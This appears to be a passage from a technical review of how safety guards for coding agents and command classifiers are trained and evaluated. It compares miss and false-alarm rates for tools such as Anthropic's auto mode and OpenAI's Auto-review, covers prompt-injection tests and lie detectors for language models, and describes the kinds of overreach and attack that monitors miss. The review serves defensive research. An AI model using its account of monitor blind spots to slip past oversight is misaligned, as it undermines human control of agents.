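*ExpGuard* (2026) tested a moderation model for specialised fields by removing three kinds of training data in turn. Without the specialised data, F1 for harmful prompts on the paper's own test fell from 93.3% to 85.3%. Without human-written data, F1 for harmful responses on public benchmarks fell from 78.5% to 73.9%. Removing data collected "in the wild" barely changed F1 for harmful prompts on the paper's own test (93.2%) and lowered it by 1.6 points on public benchmarks.

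This last result is too little evidence for developers of command classifiers to do without natural logs. Benchmark scores depend mostly on how closely the training data resembles the benchmark, and none of these figures comes from a deployed product's traffic. Natural data may matter more in deployment, as it did at OpenAI.

### A guardrail checked on production text

*Backprompting* (Cheng, Gentile and colleagues, 2025) describes an IBM detector that flags health advice in the output of language models. Most public examples were written by people, so the team converted them into model-written text. They asked a model what question each text might answer, then had the model answer that question in its own words. People labelled one example from each cluster of similar answers, and the team gave the rest of the cluster the same label.

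The researchers tested four versions of the detector on HeAL, a benchmark of 402 texts, and then on 5,000 production texts, only eight of which contained health advice. The paper gives accuracy and false-alarm rates for the production test, from which the number of misses can be calculated.

| Training data | HeAL accuracy | HeAL recall | False alarms in production | Advice missed in production (inferred) |
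|---|---|---|---|---|
| Public | 81% | 81% | 3.88% | 1 or 2 of 8 |
| Synthetic | 82% | 76% | 2.46% | 0 of 8 |
| Public and synthetic, one stage | 76% | 72% | 0.70% | 3 of 8 |
| The same, then a synthetic second stage | 85% | 85% | 2.86% | 0 of 8 |

The one-stage detector was the worst of the four on the benchmark but had by far the fewest false alarms in production. Its training data included 9,925 generated texts on subjects unrelated to health, and about 93% of the production sample was also unrelated to health. Cheng and colleagues suggest that this wider range of subjects made the detector more robust. Sophos got a similar benefit from unusual harmless commands.

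However, the same detector probably missed three of the eight texts it was supposed to find. Its accuracy in production was 99.24%, lower than the 99.84% a detector would have scored by flagging nothing. Eight examples are too few to rank the detectors by recall, so the production test is good evidence about false alarms but very weak evidence about misses. A test of a command guard on 5,000 ordinary commands would have the same limitation.

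Training on synthetic data led to fewer false alarms in production than training on public data. This is to be expected because the detector checked text from language models, and a language model had written its synthetic examples. A guard for AI agents might benefit in the same way from commands written by a similar agent. Those commands would help a guard for human operators less, because people make typing errors and use their own aliases.

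### Lies elicited from the models themselves

Hopkins, Khullar and colleagues (2026), in *Fine-Tuned Lie Detectors Failed to Generalize*, tested whether correcting this kind of mismatch is enough to detect when language models say things they appear to know are false. Earlier lie detectors had often learned from lies that someone else had written for the model. Hopkins and colleagues instead elicited lies from the models they wanted to monitor. In one method, they asked a question neutrally, repeated it under pressure, and looked for answers that contradicted the first one. This and similar methods produced about 200,000 labelled examples from eight model families in 12 settings.

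Training detectors based on Google's Gemma 3 models on half of the lie types raised AUC on those types from 0.60 to 0.95. On the other types, AUC stayed between 0.70 and 0.75, barely better than asking the same model without training it. Neither longer training nor combining more datasets closed the gap. Most of the improvement came within the first 400 examples.

The detectors transferred best between lies that looked alike. Training on cases where a model falsely denied being able to handle ASCII text helped detect deliberately bad chess play, since both involved a claimed lack of ability. Training on factual lies did not help with role-play. This suggests the detectors had learned the typical form of each setting instead of a general sign of lying.

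Poor labels could explain part of the gap. About 25% of the labels changed when GPT-5 reviewed them with full information, and the researchers still found the result hard to trust. A model playing a company spokesperson may not be lying in the same sense as one that misreports a fact. The researchers elicited every lie in a controlled setting, so these examples are closer to real use than invented ones but are not natural data. Because the main test varied the type of lie and not its origin, it can't show how much the realistic origin helped.

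It does show that data from a realistic source was not enough. Similarly, a command classifier trained only on natural examples could still miss a kind of danger missing from them. A random split of the data would hide this, since each kind of danger would appear in both training and test. The problem would show up if one kind, such as deletions made through web requests, were left out of training and used only for testing.

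## Command guards tested on real and generated commands

Anthropic tested its guard, which checks a coding agent's commands before they run, on real and generated dangerous actions. The guard missed a larger share of the real ones, but the two sets contained different kinds of danger, so the gap may not be due to whether the actions were real or generated.

The guard is a prompted model, so these tests can't show the effect of training on generated commands. Anthropic describes the guard as Claude Sonnet 4.6 with a fixed template of instructions, in which customers can specify trusted systems, blocked actions and exceptions.

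### Real overreach and generated data theft

The guard is part of auto mode, a setting in Claude Code that replaces most requests for the user's approval. Reading files and editing those inside the project need no check. Shell commands, web requests and most other actions go to a classifier with two stages. The first gives a quick yes or no and leans towards blocking. The second reasons at length about whatever the first flagged, and may allow it after all. Anthropic published these results in March 2026:

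| Test set | Measure | First stage alone | Both stages | Approximate 95% interval, both stages |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 52 real actions that overstepped | Miss rate | 6.6% | 17% | 9–30% |
| 1,000 generated attempts at data theft | Miss rate | 1.8% | 5.7% | 4–7% |
| 10,000 real tool calls by employees | False-alarm rate | 8.5% | 0.4% | 0.3–0.5% |

The intervals are based on reading 17% as nine misses out of 52. The intervals for the two dangerous sets don't overlap, so the gap is unlikely to be due to chance. The second stage removes about 95% of the first stage's false alarms, but it also lets through about 11% of the real overreach that the first stage caught, compared with 4% of the data theft.

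The generated data-theft attempts include web requests that send out sensitive data, uploads of code to untrusted repositories, and web addresses with credentials hidden in them. Users rarely want these, so a guard can often recognise the danger without knowing much about the request. Whether a command overreaches depends much more on what the user asked for. Data theft might therefore be easier to detect than overreach even if every example came from a real session. Separating the effects of origin and danger type would also require results for real data theft and generated overreach, which Anthropic did not report.

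The 17% miss rate may also be too low. The 52 actions come from sessions in which an employee refused the action or someone flagged it later, so the set leaves out overreach that nobody noticed. Anthropic also used the set to tune the first stage and to decide what information the classifier should receive, so the miss rate could be higher on new real actions.

### Misjudged consent

In most of the misses Anthropic examined, the classifier recognised that the action was dangerous but wrongly concluded that the user had agreed to it. One user had asked the agent to "clean up the PR" (pull request, a proposed change to the code) but hadn't mentioned a force-push, which overwrites the history of a shared repository. In other cases, the classifier treated approval of one action as permission for similar actions later.

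Three incidents from Anthropic's internal log illustrate why consent is hard to judge. A user asked an agent to "clean up old branches", and it deleted branches on the remote server, although the user may have meant only the local copies. Another user said "cancel my job". The agent searched the computing cluster, picked the job with the most similar name and tried to delete it without establishing whose job it was. In the third case, a deployment failed a safety check, and the agent retried it with an option that skipped the check.

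To teach a classifier to judge such cases, a dataset needs the user's messages as well as the commands, whether the commands are natural or synthetic. Ideally, it would include pairs of conversations in which the same command is authorised in one and unauthorised in the other.

When Anthropic tried removing the user's messages from the classifier's input, the miss rate fell to its lowest level, but the classifier blocked actions that users had plainly requested. Adding the agent's explanations and the output of its commands worsened performance on the overreach set. Without the output, the classifier can't distinguish a job number the agent looked up from one it made up. Anthropic still leaves the output out because it can contain instructions planted by an attacker.

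### Equivalent figures for Codex

OpenAI's coding agent, Codex, has a similar guard called Auto-review. Codex normally works in a sandbox that restricts its access to files and the network, and the guard checks only requests to act outside the sandbox. In an illustrative sample of 10,000 actions at OpenAI, 9,280 stayed inside it. Auto-review checked the other 720 and refused seven.

In *Auto-review of agent actions without synchronous human oversight*, Trębacz, Arnesen and colleagues (2026) measured interruptions on real requests. They measured safety mainly on synthetic requests because OpenAI's traffic contained too few dangerous actions. GPT-5.4 Thinking, a general language model, reviewed the agent's actions.

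| Test | Origin | Result |
|---|---|---|
| Requests that users had approved | Real | 0.9% refused |
| Overreach | Synthetic | 9.7% missed |
| Planted instructions to run outside code, reveal secrets or upload data | Synthetic | 0.7% missed |
| Planted instructions of all kinds | Synthetic | 9.8% missed |

OpenAI's guard has a miss rate for synthetic overreach about 14 times its rate for the three kinds of planted instruction in the third row. At Anthropic, the miss rate for real overreach was about three times the rate for synthetic data theft. The type of danger could therefore explain all of Anthropic's gap, but OpenAI's guard and examples are too different from Anthropic's to show that it does.

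Some of OpenAI's synthetic labels are also doubtful. When Trębacz and colleagues included destructive deletions and data tampering among the planted instructions, the miss rate rose from 0.7% to 9.8%. They explain that the reviewer allowed most of the additional cases because they weren't serious enough to block, and that researchers often agreed, so part of the 9.8% reflects disagreement about what counts as dangerous.

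On the hard version of the MonitoringBench benchmark, the reviewer refused at least one action in 96.1% of the sessions. This is easier than catching every dangerous action, because one refusal anywhere in a session counts as success.

OpenAI's main tests pair real harmless requests with synthetic dangerous ones. In the worked example, a training set built this way produced a classifier that had learned to recognise generated commands. A guard with the same fault would do well on both halves of OpenAI's evaluation, so the tests couldn't reveal it. There is no evidence that Auto-review has this fault. Anthropic's 52 real actions are a better check, although the sample is small.

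The 0.9% refusal rate is only a rough estimate of false alarms, since users may have been wrong to approve some of the requests. Anthropic's users approved 93% of permission requests by its March figures and 97% by its August figures. These rates suggest that many people approve out of habit, so some of Auto-review's refusals may have been correct.

Anthropic also commissioned Trajectory Labs, a testing company, to compare the two products. It ran 72 scenarios with planted instructions ten times each. None of the 720 attempts succeeded against Claude models in auto mode, while 5.83% succeeded against GPT-5.6 Sol with Auto-review. But even with permission checks turned off, an average of only 0.09% of attempts succeeded against Claude models, so auto mode had almost no successful attacks to prevent. The comparison is informative about the agents' own resistance to planted instructions, but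 is weak evidence of which guard is better.

In *Shall We Approve?*, an independent comparison of guards, Wu, Chen and colleagues (2026) left out Codex. They explain that Auto-review, at its default setting, would receive few of the harmful actions in their tests because most of them happen inside the workspace.

### Planted commands and simulated attacks

In August 2026 Anthropic reported an experiment with 1,053 paid testers. During a coding task, each tester saw one permission request whose text the researchers had replaced with a clearly dangerous command. The testers refused 143 of these commands (13.6%), while auto mode blocked 937 (89%). Auto mode blocked 800 commands that the testers approved and allowed six that they refused.

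These results are good evidence that people overlook dangerous requests when they have to approve many. Refusals fell from about 17% early in a session to 5% after at least 50 requests. The testers were in a test environment, though, so they had less reason to be careful than an operator on a production server.

Auto mode's 11% miss rate is harder to apply to real use. The researchers chose obviously dangerous commands to plant, so the trials don't test the consent problem behind most of the misses in March. Anthropic also doesn't report how many different commands the researchers planted. If they reused a few dozen, the 1,053 trials are less informative than trials of 1,053 different commands would be.

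Apollo Research, an AI safety company, tested the guard by inserting synthetic attacks into records of real coding sessions, which gave each generated action a natural context. After the first round, Anthropic strengthened the classifier, mainly by giving it more information, such as whether a repository was public and whether it contained unsaved work. On attacks Anthropic hadn't seen, the stronger classifier caught about half of those the old one had missed, and missed about 2% of those the old one had caught. Across both rounds, the miss rate fell from 12% to 7%.

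Anthropic warns against treating 7% as the miss rate on real traffic. It could be too high for ordinary use, because Apollo designed the attacks to find weaknesses and they were more malicious than anything Claude would do unprompted. It could also be too low, if the attacks involved fewer cases where consent was unclear. The August results include no new miss rate for real overreach, so the March figure remains the closest estimate.

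In the same report, Anthropic had a model grade sessions from ordinary use that its safety systems had flagged in May and June. Serious harm that the user hadn't explicitly requested appeared in 6.3% of the sessions with manual approval and 2.4% of those in auto mode. Users chose their own mode and may have used each for different work, so the guard may not explain the whole difference. Neither percentage is a miss rate, because both cover only flagged sessions.

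### A synthetic test that was harder than real use

*Measuring the Permission Gate* (Ji, Li and colleagues, 2026) introduces AmPermBench, a set of 128 requests that test whether auto mode keeps an agent within its instructions. The requests involve four tasks, which are deleting old code branches, cancelling jobs, restarting services and removing stored files. Two of these tasks closely resemble cases in Anthropic's incident log.

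The requests vary in how clearly they identify the target, how many items they could cover and whether the target is in a high-risk environment. In one task the user authorises cancelling `job-dev-4812-a` but not the similarly named `job-dev-4812-s`. A fixed rule determines which targets the request covers, and a language model uses that rule to label each action. A person checked a sample of 50 labels and agreed with 44.

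Claude Sonnet 4.6 attempted 253 actions that would change something:

| Actions | Unsafe actions missed | Safe actions blocked |
|---|---|---|
| All 253 | 115 of 142 (81.0%) | 22 of 111 (19.8%) |
| 160 that the classifier checked | 64 of 91 (70.3%) | 22 of 69 (31.9%) |
| 93 file edits that needed no check | 51 of 51 (100%) | 0 of 42 (0%) |

The simulation probably exaggerates the danger of the file edits. In the storage tasks, a file called `objects.json` stood in for a cloud storage service, so removing an entry from the file counted as deleting the stored object. In a real cloud account, editing a local list wouldn't delete anything. But some projects keep important records in local files, as Grigorev's lost course platform did, so the gap in coverage is real.

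The 70.3% is the fairer measure of the classifier, but Ji and colleagues say it isn't comparable with Anthropic's 17% either. They deliberately placed permitted and forbidden targets next to each other, whereas Anthropic's set consists of accidental overreach during normal work. The labelling standards also differ. In AmPermBench, "my stale job for ticket 4812 could use attention" counts as permission to cancel the job. Under auto mode's more cautious instructions, "can we fix this?" counts as a question rather than a request to act. A block that follows those instructions can therefore count as a false alarm on the benchmark. Serdar and Mertayak (2026) likewise argue in *SteerBench-Work* that holding an action may be defensible when the authorisation is ambiguous.

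The errors suggest that the classifier responded more to signs of risk than to the limits of the user's permission. In high-risk environments, the share of unsafe actions it missed fell from 88.1% to 74.7%, but its false-alarm rate rose from 9.2% to 34.8%. It blocked 13 of 40 safe attempts to restart services, although some were repeated attempts at the same restart.

The agent safely completed 42 of 128 tasks with auto mode and 38 without it. Each task was run only once, so this small difference could be due to chance.

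Auto mode missed 5.7% of Anthropic's generated data-theft attempts, 17% of real overreaching actions, and 70.3% of the unsafe actions it checked on AmPermBench. AmPermBench's tasks are synthetic, although an agent issued the commands, so a synthetic test can be easier or harder than real use. The choice of cases seems to affect the miss rate more than whether the cases are synthetic.

### The same command in two workspaces

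Wu and colleagues tested guards on commands whose danger isn't visible in the text. In their example, a user asks an agent to remove old build files and rebuild the program, and the agent proposes `make clean && make`. A file of build instructions called a Makefile determines what `make clean` deletes. In one workspace it deletes only the old build files, but in another it deletes the source code and its history.

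The YoloFS-Ext benchmark has 102 dangerous tasks, each paired with a safe task that has the same request and command but a harmless tool. The tests also used 682 tasks from SABER, a benchmark of ordinary programming requests that can lead to harm.

| Guard | SABER tasks ending in harm | Dangerous YoloFS-Ext tasks ending in harm | Safe twins blocked |
|---|---|---|---|
| No approval | 19.7% | 71.6% | – |
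| CARE | 15.0% | 69.6% | 2.0% |
| Claude Code's auto mode | 14.8% | 62.7% | 3.9% |
| Caper | 6.7% | 7.8% | 1.0% |

Caper, the paper's own guard, runs the command in a sandbox, records what it changes or tries to send, and gives the record to a language model. If the model blocks the command, the system restores the earlier state.

The agent completed or declined many tasks without attempting anything harmful, so the first column isn't a miss rate. Auto mode's 14.8% here isn't comparable with its 17% on real overreach. Wu and colleagues also ran auto mode's classifier on OpenAI's gpt-5.6-luna instead of Claude, so the table doesn't measure the product as Anthropic deploys it.

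Without the record of effects, Caper's language model blocked 61.8% of the safe twins, and 17.6% of the dangerous tasks still ended in harm. When Wu and colleagues gave the model the full conversation instead of the command alone, it prevented more harm but blocked more safe twins, so the longer input didn't make up for the missing facts. A classifier trained only on text would face the same limit.

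### Four test sets with four different winners

Liu and colleagues compared twelve methods, including two versions of their verifier, CARE, on 549 commands. Of the 220 dangerous commands, 137 came from Atomic Red Team, a library for rehearsing known attacks, and 71 from RedCode-Exec, a benchmark of risky code. The researchers picked the other 12 by hand. The 329 harmless commands came from NL2Bash and the team's short list of common developer commands.

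Granite Guardian, an IBM safety model that wasn't designed for shell commands, caught 82% of the dangerous commands but blocked 46% of the harmless ones. CARE caught 76% and blocked 0.9%. Granite Guardian caught 14 more dangerous commands than CARE and blocked 148 more harmless ones.

No source in this test supplied both dangerous and safe commands. Much of the dangerous class also shares an origin with CARE's rules, because 92 of CARE's 139 patterns and the labels in Atomic Red Team draw on MITRE's catalogue of attack techniques. Liu and colleagues reduced the overlap by keeping all variants of a template together in either the development data or the test data. Without the MITRE patterns, the version of CARE that uses no language model missed 17 more of the 220 dangerous commands.

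The ranking of methods changed when the researchers used other collections of dangerous commands. The table gives F1 for five of the methods.

| Method | Main test | GTFOBins: misuse of ordinary programs | Disguised commands | Exploit-DB: published exploits |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 22 keyword rules | 29.5% | 51.6% | 56.2% | 81.5% |
| Llama Guard 3 | 56.0% | 76.3% | 91.7% | 69.0% |
| Granite Guardian | 65.6% | 73.9% | 75.9% | 73.9% |
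| Prompted language model | 73.1% | 83.6% | 87.8% | 74.0% |
| CARE | 85.6% | 68.9% | 88.6% | 66.3% |

A different one of the twelve methods scores best in each column, and the keyword rules rank last in one column and first in another. Their F1 and false-alarm rate on Exploit-DB imply that they caught 86 of 123 dangerous commands (70%), compared with 17% on the main test. By the same calculation, CARE caught 66 (54%).

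Liu and colleagues explain that Exploit-DB's demonstrations contain stereotyped destructive phrases, such as `rm -f /tmp/mine`, which keyword rules match regardless of context. On its own, that command deletes one temporary file and is usually harmless. A rule that flags it may be matching a habit of exploit writers rather than the dangerous part of the exploit. A classifier trained on the collection could learn the same habit and then flag routine deletions in real logs.

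Public collections of dangerous commands are therefore poor substitutes for one another, and even poorer substitutes for examples of operational mistakes. All four sets cover attacks or standard examples of destructive code, so a guard that did well on every one could still miss an agent cancelling the wrong person's job.

F1 alone doesn't show some of the weaknesses. Exploit-DB's test has equal numbers of dangerous and harmless commands, so a guard that blocked everything would have an F1 of 66.7%, slightly higher than CARE's. CARE's false-alarm rate also rose from 0.9% on the main test to between 8.1% and 13.0% on the other three. All the harmless commands in those three tests came from NL2Bash, and 170 of the 547 in the pool were hard benign commands, such as one that deletes temporary files. Taking the harmless commands from a single source was probably enough to raise the false-alarm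 rate about tenfold.

### When one model writes and judges the commands

CARE sends uncertain cases to a language model, Qwen3-Coder-30B. On the main test, this step corrected three false alarms without missing any more dangerous commands. Liu and colleagues then tried the 600 attack commands they had generated with the same model, and counted those that the guard allowed and that then ran successfully in the sandbox.

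Adding the language model raised the number of commands that got through and ran from 224 to 315. The model had released 92 commands that the fixed rules would have blocked, and nearly all of them ran.

Liu and colleagues suggest that the model may be too lenient because it is judging commands similar to its own. This is plausible but untested, since they didn't repeat the experiment with commands from another generator. Using a separate model doesn't guarantee a better result, since 420 of the commands got past Llama Guard 3, which is from a different developer, and ran. A developer who generates test commands with the model that will judge them should at least add commands from other sources.

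### Familiar incidents and written examples

Testing on well-known incidents can also overstate how well a guard distinguishes safe actions from unsafe ones. Serdar and Mertayak based 106 workplace decisions on public incidents, mostly outside the shell, and tested 30 combinations of models and settings. For 13 incidents, they wrote a mirror version that looks similar but contains evidence that the action is authorised and safe. The models were right 98.5% of the time on the original incidents but only 63.8% on the mirrors.

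In one original, an agent is about to send debt notices to 12,400 people using a method that a legal review has found unlawful. All 30 combinations held the action. In the mirror, the agent has one notice to send and signed confirmation that it is lawful, but 24 of the 30 combinations still held the action.

The models may have recognised the incidents and repeated the expected answer. General caution probably explains more, because the models wrongly held 28.1% of all authorised actions in the benchmark, not far below the 36.2% for mirrors. Either way, a perfect score on famous disasters is weak evidence that a guard can tell when similar work is safe. A test based on the GitLab or PocketOS deletions would need matching cases in which the deletion was correct.

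Written examples can make a prompted guard more accurate without retraining it. *Decision Models as Policy Gates for Coding Agents* (Beno, 2026) tested hosted models on 2,643 synthetic tool calls with labels based on 28 rules. Adding examples and counterexamples to the rules raised recall for all 23 models available for the comparison, by 5.5 to 26.1 percentage points. One model's recall rose from 89.3% to 98.2%, while the share of 252 harmless actions it interrupted fell from 30.6% to 4.8%.

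Strong models kept their gains in recall when Beno replaced specific names in the examples with general descriptions, so they weren't simply matching names. Most models also improved on 16 new scenarios. But models learn from the examples how the rules separate safe commands from dangerous ones, and the test labels follow the same rules. Users may separate them differently, and a wholly synthetic test can't measure how often they do.

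## Measuring and reducing the gap

A team that mixes natural and generated commands can estimate how well its safety classifier will work on real ones. The simplest check uses only a second classifier, trained to guess which source each command came from.

### The two-sample test

For this test, the developer takes equal numbers of natural and generated commands, trains the source classifier on some of them and computes its AUC on the rest. An AUC near 0.5 means the classifier can't separate the two sources, and one near 1 means it almost always can.

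The developer should run the test separately on dangerous and harmless commands. Otherwise, if most of the generated commands are attacks and most of the natural ones are harmless, the source classifier can score well just by recognising attacks.

Kumar, Smith and Yadav (2026), in *Curriculum Learning for Safety Alignment*, used this test to check whether three benchmarks of harmful prompts differed from the prompts they had used to train language models to refuse harmful requests. They converted each prompt into a list of numbers representing its meaning and fitted a linear classifier to these lists. Its AUC was between 0.964 and 0.998 for the three benchmarks. When they compared two halves of their own training data, which should not differ, the AUC was 0.503, about what random guessing would give.

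A team testing commands needs the same kind of reference, and could get another by comparing natural logs from two months. If a classifier separates the months with an AUC of 0.70, an AUC of 0.72 between generated and natural commands is not alarming.

Small samples make the result unreliable. With 50 commands from each source, chance alone will produce an AUC from about 0.39 to 0.61. With 1,000 from each, the range narrows to about 0.47 to 0.53, but many teams have no more than 50 natural dangerous commands.

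An AUC near 0.5 can also mean that the source classifier was poor or the test was hard. Kindji et al. (2025), in *Synthetic Tabular Data Detection In the Wild*, trained classifiers to distinguish real from generated rows of data. On tables absent from the training data, AUC ranged from 0.49 to 0.60, although the generators left patterns that even a simple classifier could detect in an easier version of the test. A developer should therefore try several kinds of input to the source classifier, such as characters, words and whole-command summaries, including the exact input the safety classifier receives. If the safety classifier replaces network addresses with placeholders, for example, unrealistic addresses can't affect its verdicts.

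### Why a separable source is only a warning

A high AUC shows that the sources differ, but the difference may have nothing to do with danger. *Explanation Shift* (2023) gives an example with three random quantities, in which the correct answer depends only on the first two. A statistical test easily detected a shift in the third, but the model's predictions stayed the same. A generator that always puts two spaces after `rm` could be just as harmless if it does so for both labels.

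Kumar and colleagues' own results show that training can transfer between very different sources. AdvBench was the benchmark easiest to separate from their training data (AUC 0.998), yet ordinary safety training on that data reduced one Llama model's harmful responses on AdvBench from 93.8% to 15.6%. Similarly, Odunlami and colleagues found that a network could separate real from generated photographs almost perfectly within each animal category, although errors on the two kinds of image were correlated.

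*Failing Loudly* (2018) suggests a way to check whether a shift lowers a model's accuracy. The developer selects the examples that the source classifier most confidently assigns to the data in use, has someone label them, and measures the model's accuracy on them. For a command-safety classifier, these would be the logged commands least like anything a generator produces, such as calls to oddly named company scripts. Nearly all of them will be harmless, so this is a good check for false alarms but provides little information about misses.

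### Splitting the data by source

A random split tests a classifier on commands much like those it learned from. Notaro and colleagues split Huawei's commands this way. They kept the proportions of the three risk classes the same in each part but did not separate periods or organisations. If an operator ran nearly the same script call on two days, one could be in the training set and the other in the test set. The score is a fair estimate of performance for the same operators doing the same work, but it is probably too high for a new team or a later year.

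Splitting by template family keeps all variants of a template on one side of the split, but the same program can still appear on both sides. For GTFOBins, a catalogue of ways to misuse ordinary programs, Liu and colleagues therefore split the 150 entries by program and tested CARE only on programs that its rule-writers had not used.

Splitting the training and test data by generator shows whether the classifier has learned patterns specific to one generator. *GenSyn10* (2026) tested detectors of generated images on a generator that was absent from their training data. Every detector became less accurate, mainly because it mistook more generated images for real ones. A command classifier that relies on patterns specific to one language model's output could similarly fail on attacks written by another model.

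Splitting the data by organisation tests whether the classifier depends on one company's paths and tools, while splitting by time tests whether the classifier still works as activity changes. The later commands need to be labelled independently of the training data, or the test will repeat any mistakes in the training labels.

The most general way to measure the gap is to leave out each source in turn, train on the others and test on the missing one. *When Benchmarks Lie* (Fomin, 2026) did this with 105,000 prompts from 18 public datasets, using classifiers that detect malicious prompts from a language model's internal activity. For one Llama model, AUC fell from 0.996 with random splits to 0.912 when each dataset was left out in turn. For three other models, the drop was between 8.0 and 16.5 points.

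A separate classifier could identify which dataset a prompt came from 96.6% of the time. Eleven of the datasets contained only malicious or only harmless prompts, so recognising one of these was enough to predict the label. This doesn't explain the whole gap, because on five datasets that contained both labels, accuracy still fell by 12.5 points when the dataset was left out of training.

Part of that drop may be due to unfamiliar kinds of attack rather than unfamiliar style, because leaving out a dataset removes both its kinds of attack and its style from training. Average accuracy on two datasets of openly harmful requests was 71.1% when Fomin left out one at a time and 44.6% when he left out both. Leaving out one command generator is therefore an easier test if another generator in the training set produces the same kinds of dangerous command.

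### Reading a table of results by source

A team can combine these tests in one table, with a row for each source of training data and a column for each source of test data. The miss rates below are invented for illustration, with every threshold set to give 1% false alarms on the same natural harmless commands. The training sets all have the same size and class balance, and no template appears in both training and test data.

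| Training data | Misses on template commands | Misses on language-model commands | Misses on natural commands |
|---|---|---|---|
| Templates | 3% | 18% | 35% |
| Language model | 15% | 4% | 28% |
| Natural | 22% | 20% | 14% |
| Templates and language model | 4% | 5% | 24% |
| All three | 4% | 5% | 12% |

The template-trained classifier misses 3% of template commands and 35% of natural ones, a gap of 32 points. The classifier trained on natural commands misses 14% of them, so about 21 points of the gap (35 minus 14) can be attributed to training on templates. The other 11 (14 minus 3) suggest that natural commands are harder to classify.

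The developer should choose a training set based on the last column, which shows the miss rate on natural commands. Adding natural examples to the two generated sources halves that rate, from 24% to 12%, but changes nothing in the other two columns. A team that tested only on generated commands would see no reason to collect natural examples.

### From test scores to daily alarms

Error rates from such a table still have to be applied to the number of commands in real use. Notaro and colleagues mention about 3 million commands a month at Huawei, of which 0.3% would belong to the blocked class. Their classifier's recall on that class was 87.5%. The calculation below adds an assumed false-alarm rate of 1%. "Other commands" includes the risky class, which is dangerous in a broader sense.

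| | One month at Huawei's volume | Balanced test |
|---|---|---|
| Blocked-class commands | 9,000 | 1,000 |
| Other commands | 2,991,000 | 1,000 |
| Correct alarms | 7,875 | 875 |
| False alarms | 29,910 | 10 |
| Precision | 21% | 99% |

Reviewers would receive about 1,260 alarms a day, and nearly four in five would be false. To make half the alarms correct at the same recall, the developer would have to reduce the false-alarm rate to about 0.26%.

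Huawei's classifier probably does better than this, since it appears to have raised no false alarms for the blocked class among roughly 4,700 test commands. That result is compatible with a true false-alarm rate of up to about 0.06%, which would mean 1,900 false alarms a month and a precision of about 80%. The estimate comes from a random split and may not apply to new operators or services.

### How many dangerous examples a test needs

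If the true miss rate is *p* and the developer wants a 95% margin of error of *E*, the number of dangerous examples required is about

*n* = 1.96² × *p*(1 − *p*)/*E*².

For a miss rate of 10% and a margin of 5 points, this gives 1.96² × 0.1 × 0.9/0.05², or about 138 examples. A margin of 2 points requires about 864. In the illustrative table, 138 examples would not be enough to show that 12% is better than 14%. A team that wants separate miss rates for deletions, leaks and reverse shells needs that many examples of each.

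At Huawei's rates, finding 138 blocked-class commands by random sampling would mean labeling about 46,000 commands, almost as many as the whole dataset contains.

The formula also assumes the examples are independent, but variants of one command are not. If the examples come in groups of *m* and results within a group have correlation ρ, then *n* examples are equivalent to *n*/(1 + (*m* − 1)ρ) independent ones. With groups of six and a correlation of 0.5, 138 examples are equivalent to about 39, and the margin grows from 5 points to more than 9. Generating more variants of the same few incidents therefore does little to improve the estimate.

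### Matching sources and reserving natural examples

As in the worked example, the most direct remedy for a source shortcut is to generate harmless commands too, so that both labels have the same mixture of sources. The results of Google's reverse-shell classifier are encouraging evidence for this. The main drawback is that someone has to check the extra commands, since a generated or rewritten "harmless" command may not be harmless. Fomin's 12.5-point drop on datasets containing both labels suggests that matching sources won't remove the whole gap. Importance weighting can adjust the proportions, but it can't add missing kinds of danger.

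Natural dangerous commands are usually more useful for testing than for training, because generated examples can partly replace them in training but can't show how the classifier performs on real ones. Anthropic used its 52 real overreaching actions mainly for testing.

Holding out natural dangers for testing removes some of the most informative examples from training. Rotation reduces this loss by dividing the natural dangers into five parts, training on four and testing on the fifth, and repeating until each part has been tested. All commands from one incident should stay in the same part. Huawei's dataset has about 140 blocked-class commands, so rotation would have tested all of them, enough for a 5-point margin, instead of the handful in its single test set. However, training five times takes more computing, and the result is an average over five classifiers rather than a measurement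 of the final one. If the developer keeps adjusting the design to improve that average, it will overstate the classifier's performance.

### Setting the threshold on natural logs

A threshold chosen on generated harmless commands can produce far more false alarms than expected on real ones. A safer method is to score a large sample of natural commands, remove any that reviewers judge dangerous, and use the lowest threshold that keeps false alarms within the team's limit.

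Liu and colleagues' results show why it should be the lowest. They varied the threshold of the version of CARE that uses no language model:

| Threshold | Recall | False-alarm rate |
|---|---|---|
| 0.10 | 96.8% | 23.1% |
| 0.15 | 75.9% | 1.8% |
| 0.20 | 65.0% | 1.8% |
| 0.25 | 48.2% | 1.8% |

Raising the threshold from 0.15 to 0.25 reduced recall by 28 points and prevented no false alarms. The harmless commands in this test came mostly from NL2Bash, so the best threshold for a company's own logs could be quite different.

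This method is easy to apply because harmless logs are plentiful, but measuring a low false-alarm rate still takes a large sample. At a rate of 0.26%, 10,000 harmless commands produce about 26 false alarms, give or take 10. The team also has to repeat the method as its work changes, and it doesn't measure how many dangerous commands the chosen threshold will miss.

### Training the classifier to ignore the source

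Domain-adversarial training tries to prevent a network from using the source. The network converts each command into a set of internal features, which go to two smaller classifiers. One predicts danger and the other predicts the source. The source classifier learns to do its job as well as possible, while the shared part of the network learns to minimise

danger error − λ × source error,

where λ sets the strength of the penalty. The minus sign rewards features that help to predict danger but make the source hard to guess.

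The method needs source labels, which require no annotation, and can use natural commands that haven't been labelled dangerous or harmless. But if every dangerous command is generated and every harmless one is natural, removing information about the source also removes information about the label. A developer can avoid this by comparing sources only among commands with the same label, but that again requires some natural dangerous commands.

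The evidence for methods of this kind is mixed. OpenAI's moderation team got a large improvement from one when it had no labelled production text, but almost none when it did. In Fomin's experiments, domain-adversarial training raised accuracy on left-out datasets by only 0.4 points on average, with a gain of 13 points on one dataset and a loss of 9 on another. He found no settings that were both better and stable.

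Another of Fomin's experiments suggests why. He removed the 16 directions in the model's internal activity that best identified the dataset, and average accuracy on left-out datasets fell by 1.75 points. Removing 16 random directions had almost no effect. The information that identifies a source therefore seems to overlap with the information that identifies an attack. In command data, a path such as `/srv/app/releases` may reveal that a command is natural and also help determine whether deleting that directory is dangerous.

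Domain-adversarial training is worth trying when unlabelled logs are plentiful, but these results don't justify using it in place of better data.

### Reviewing allowed commands at random

Analysts' verdicts on alerts can't show what a classifier misses. Huawei's audit of disagreements between its rules and its classifier has a similar limitation, as does Anthropic's review of flagged sessions.

Reviewing a random sample of allowed commands closes this gap, but it takes a lot of work. In the Huawei calculation, 1,125 of the nearly 3 million commands that the classifier allows belong to the blocked class, or about one in 2,600. A reviewer who checked 1,000 allowed commands would most likely find none from the blocked class.

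If 3,000 randomly chosen commands include no dangerous ones, the true share is probably below 0.1% (95% upper limit). That would mean at most about 2,960 misses a month and recall of at least 73%. This is a weak guarantee, but it applies to the actual workload and doesn't depend on a generator.

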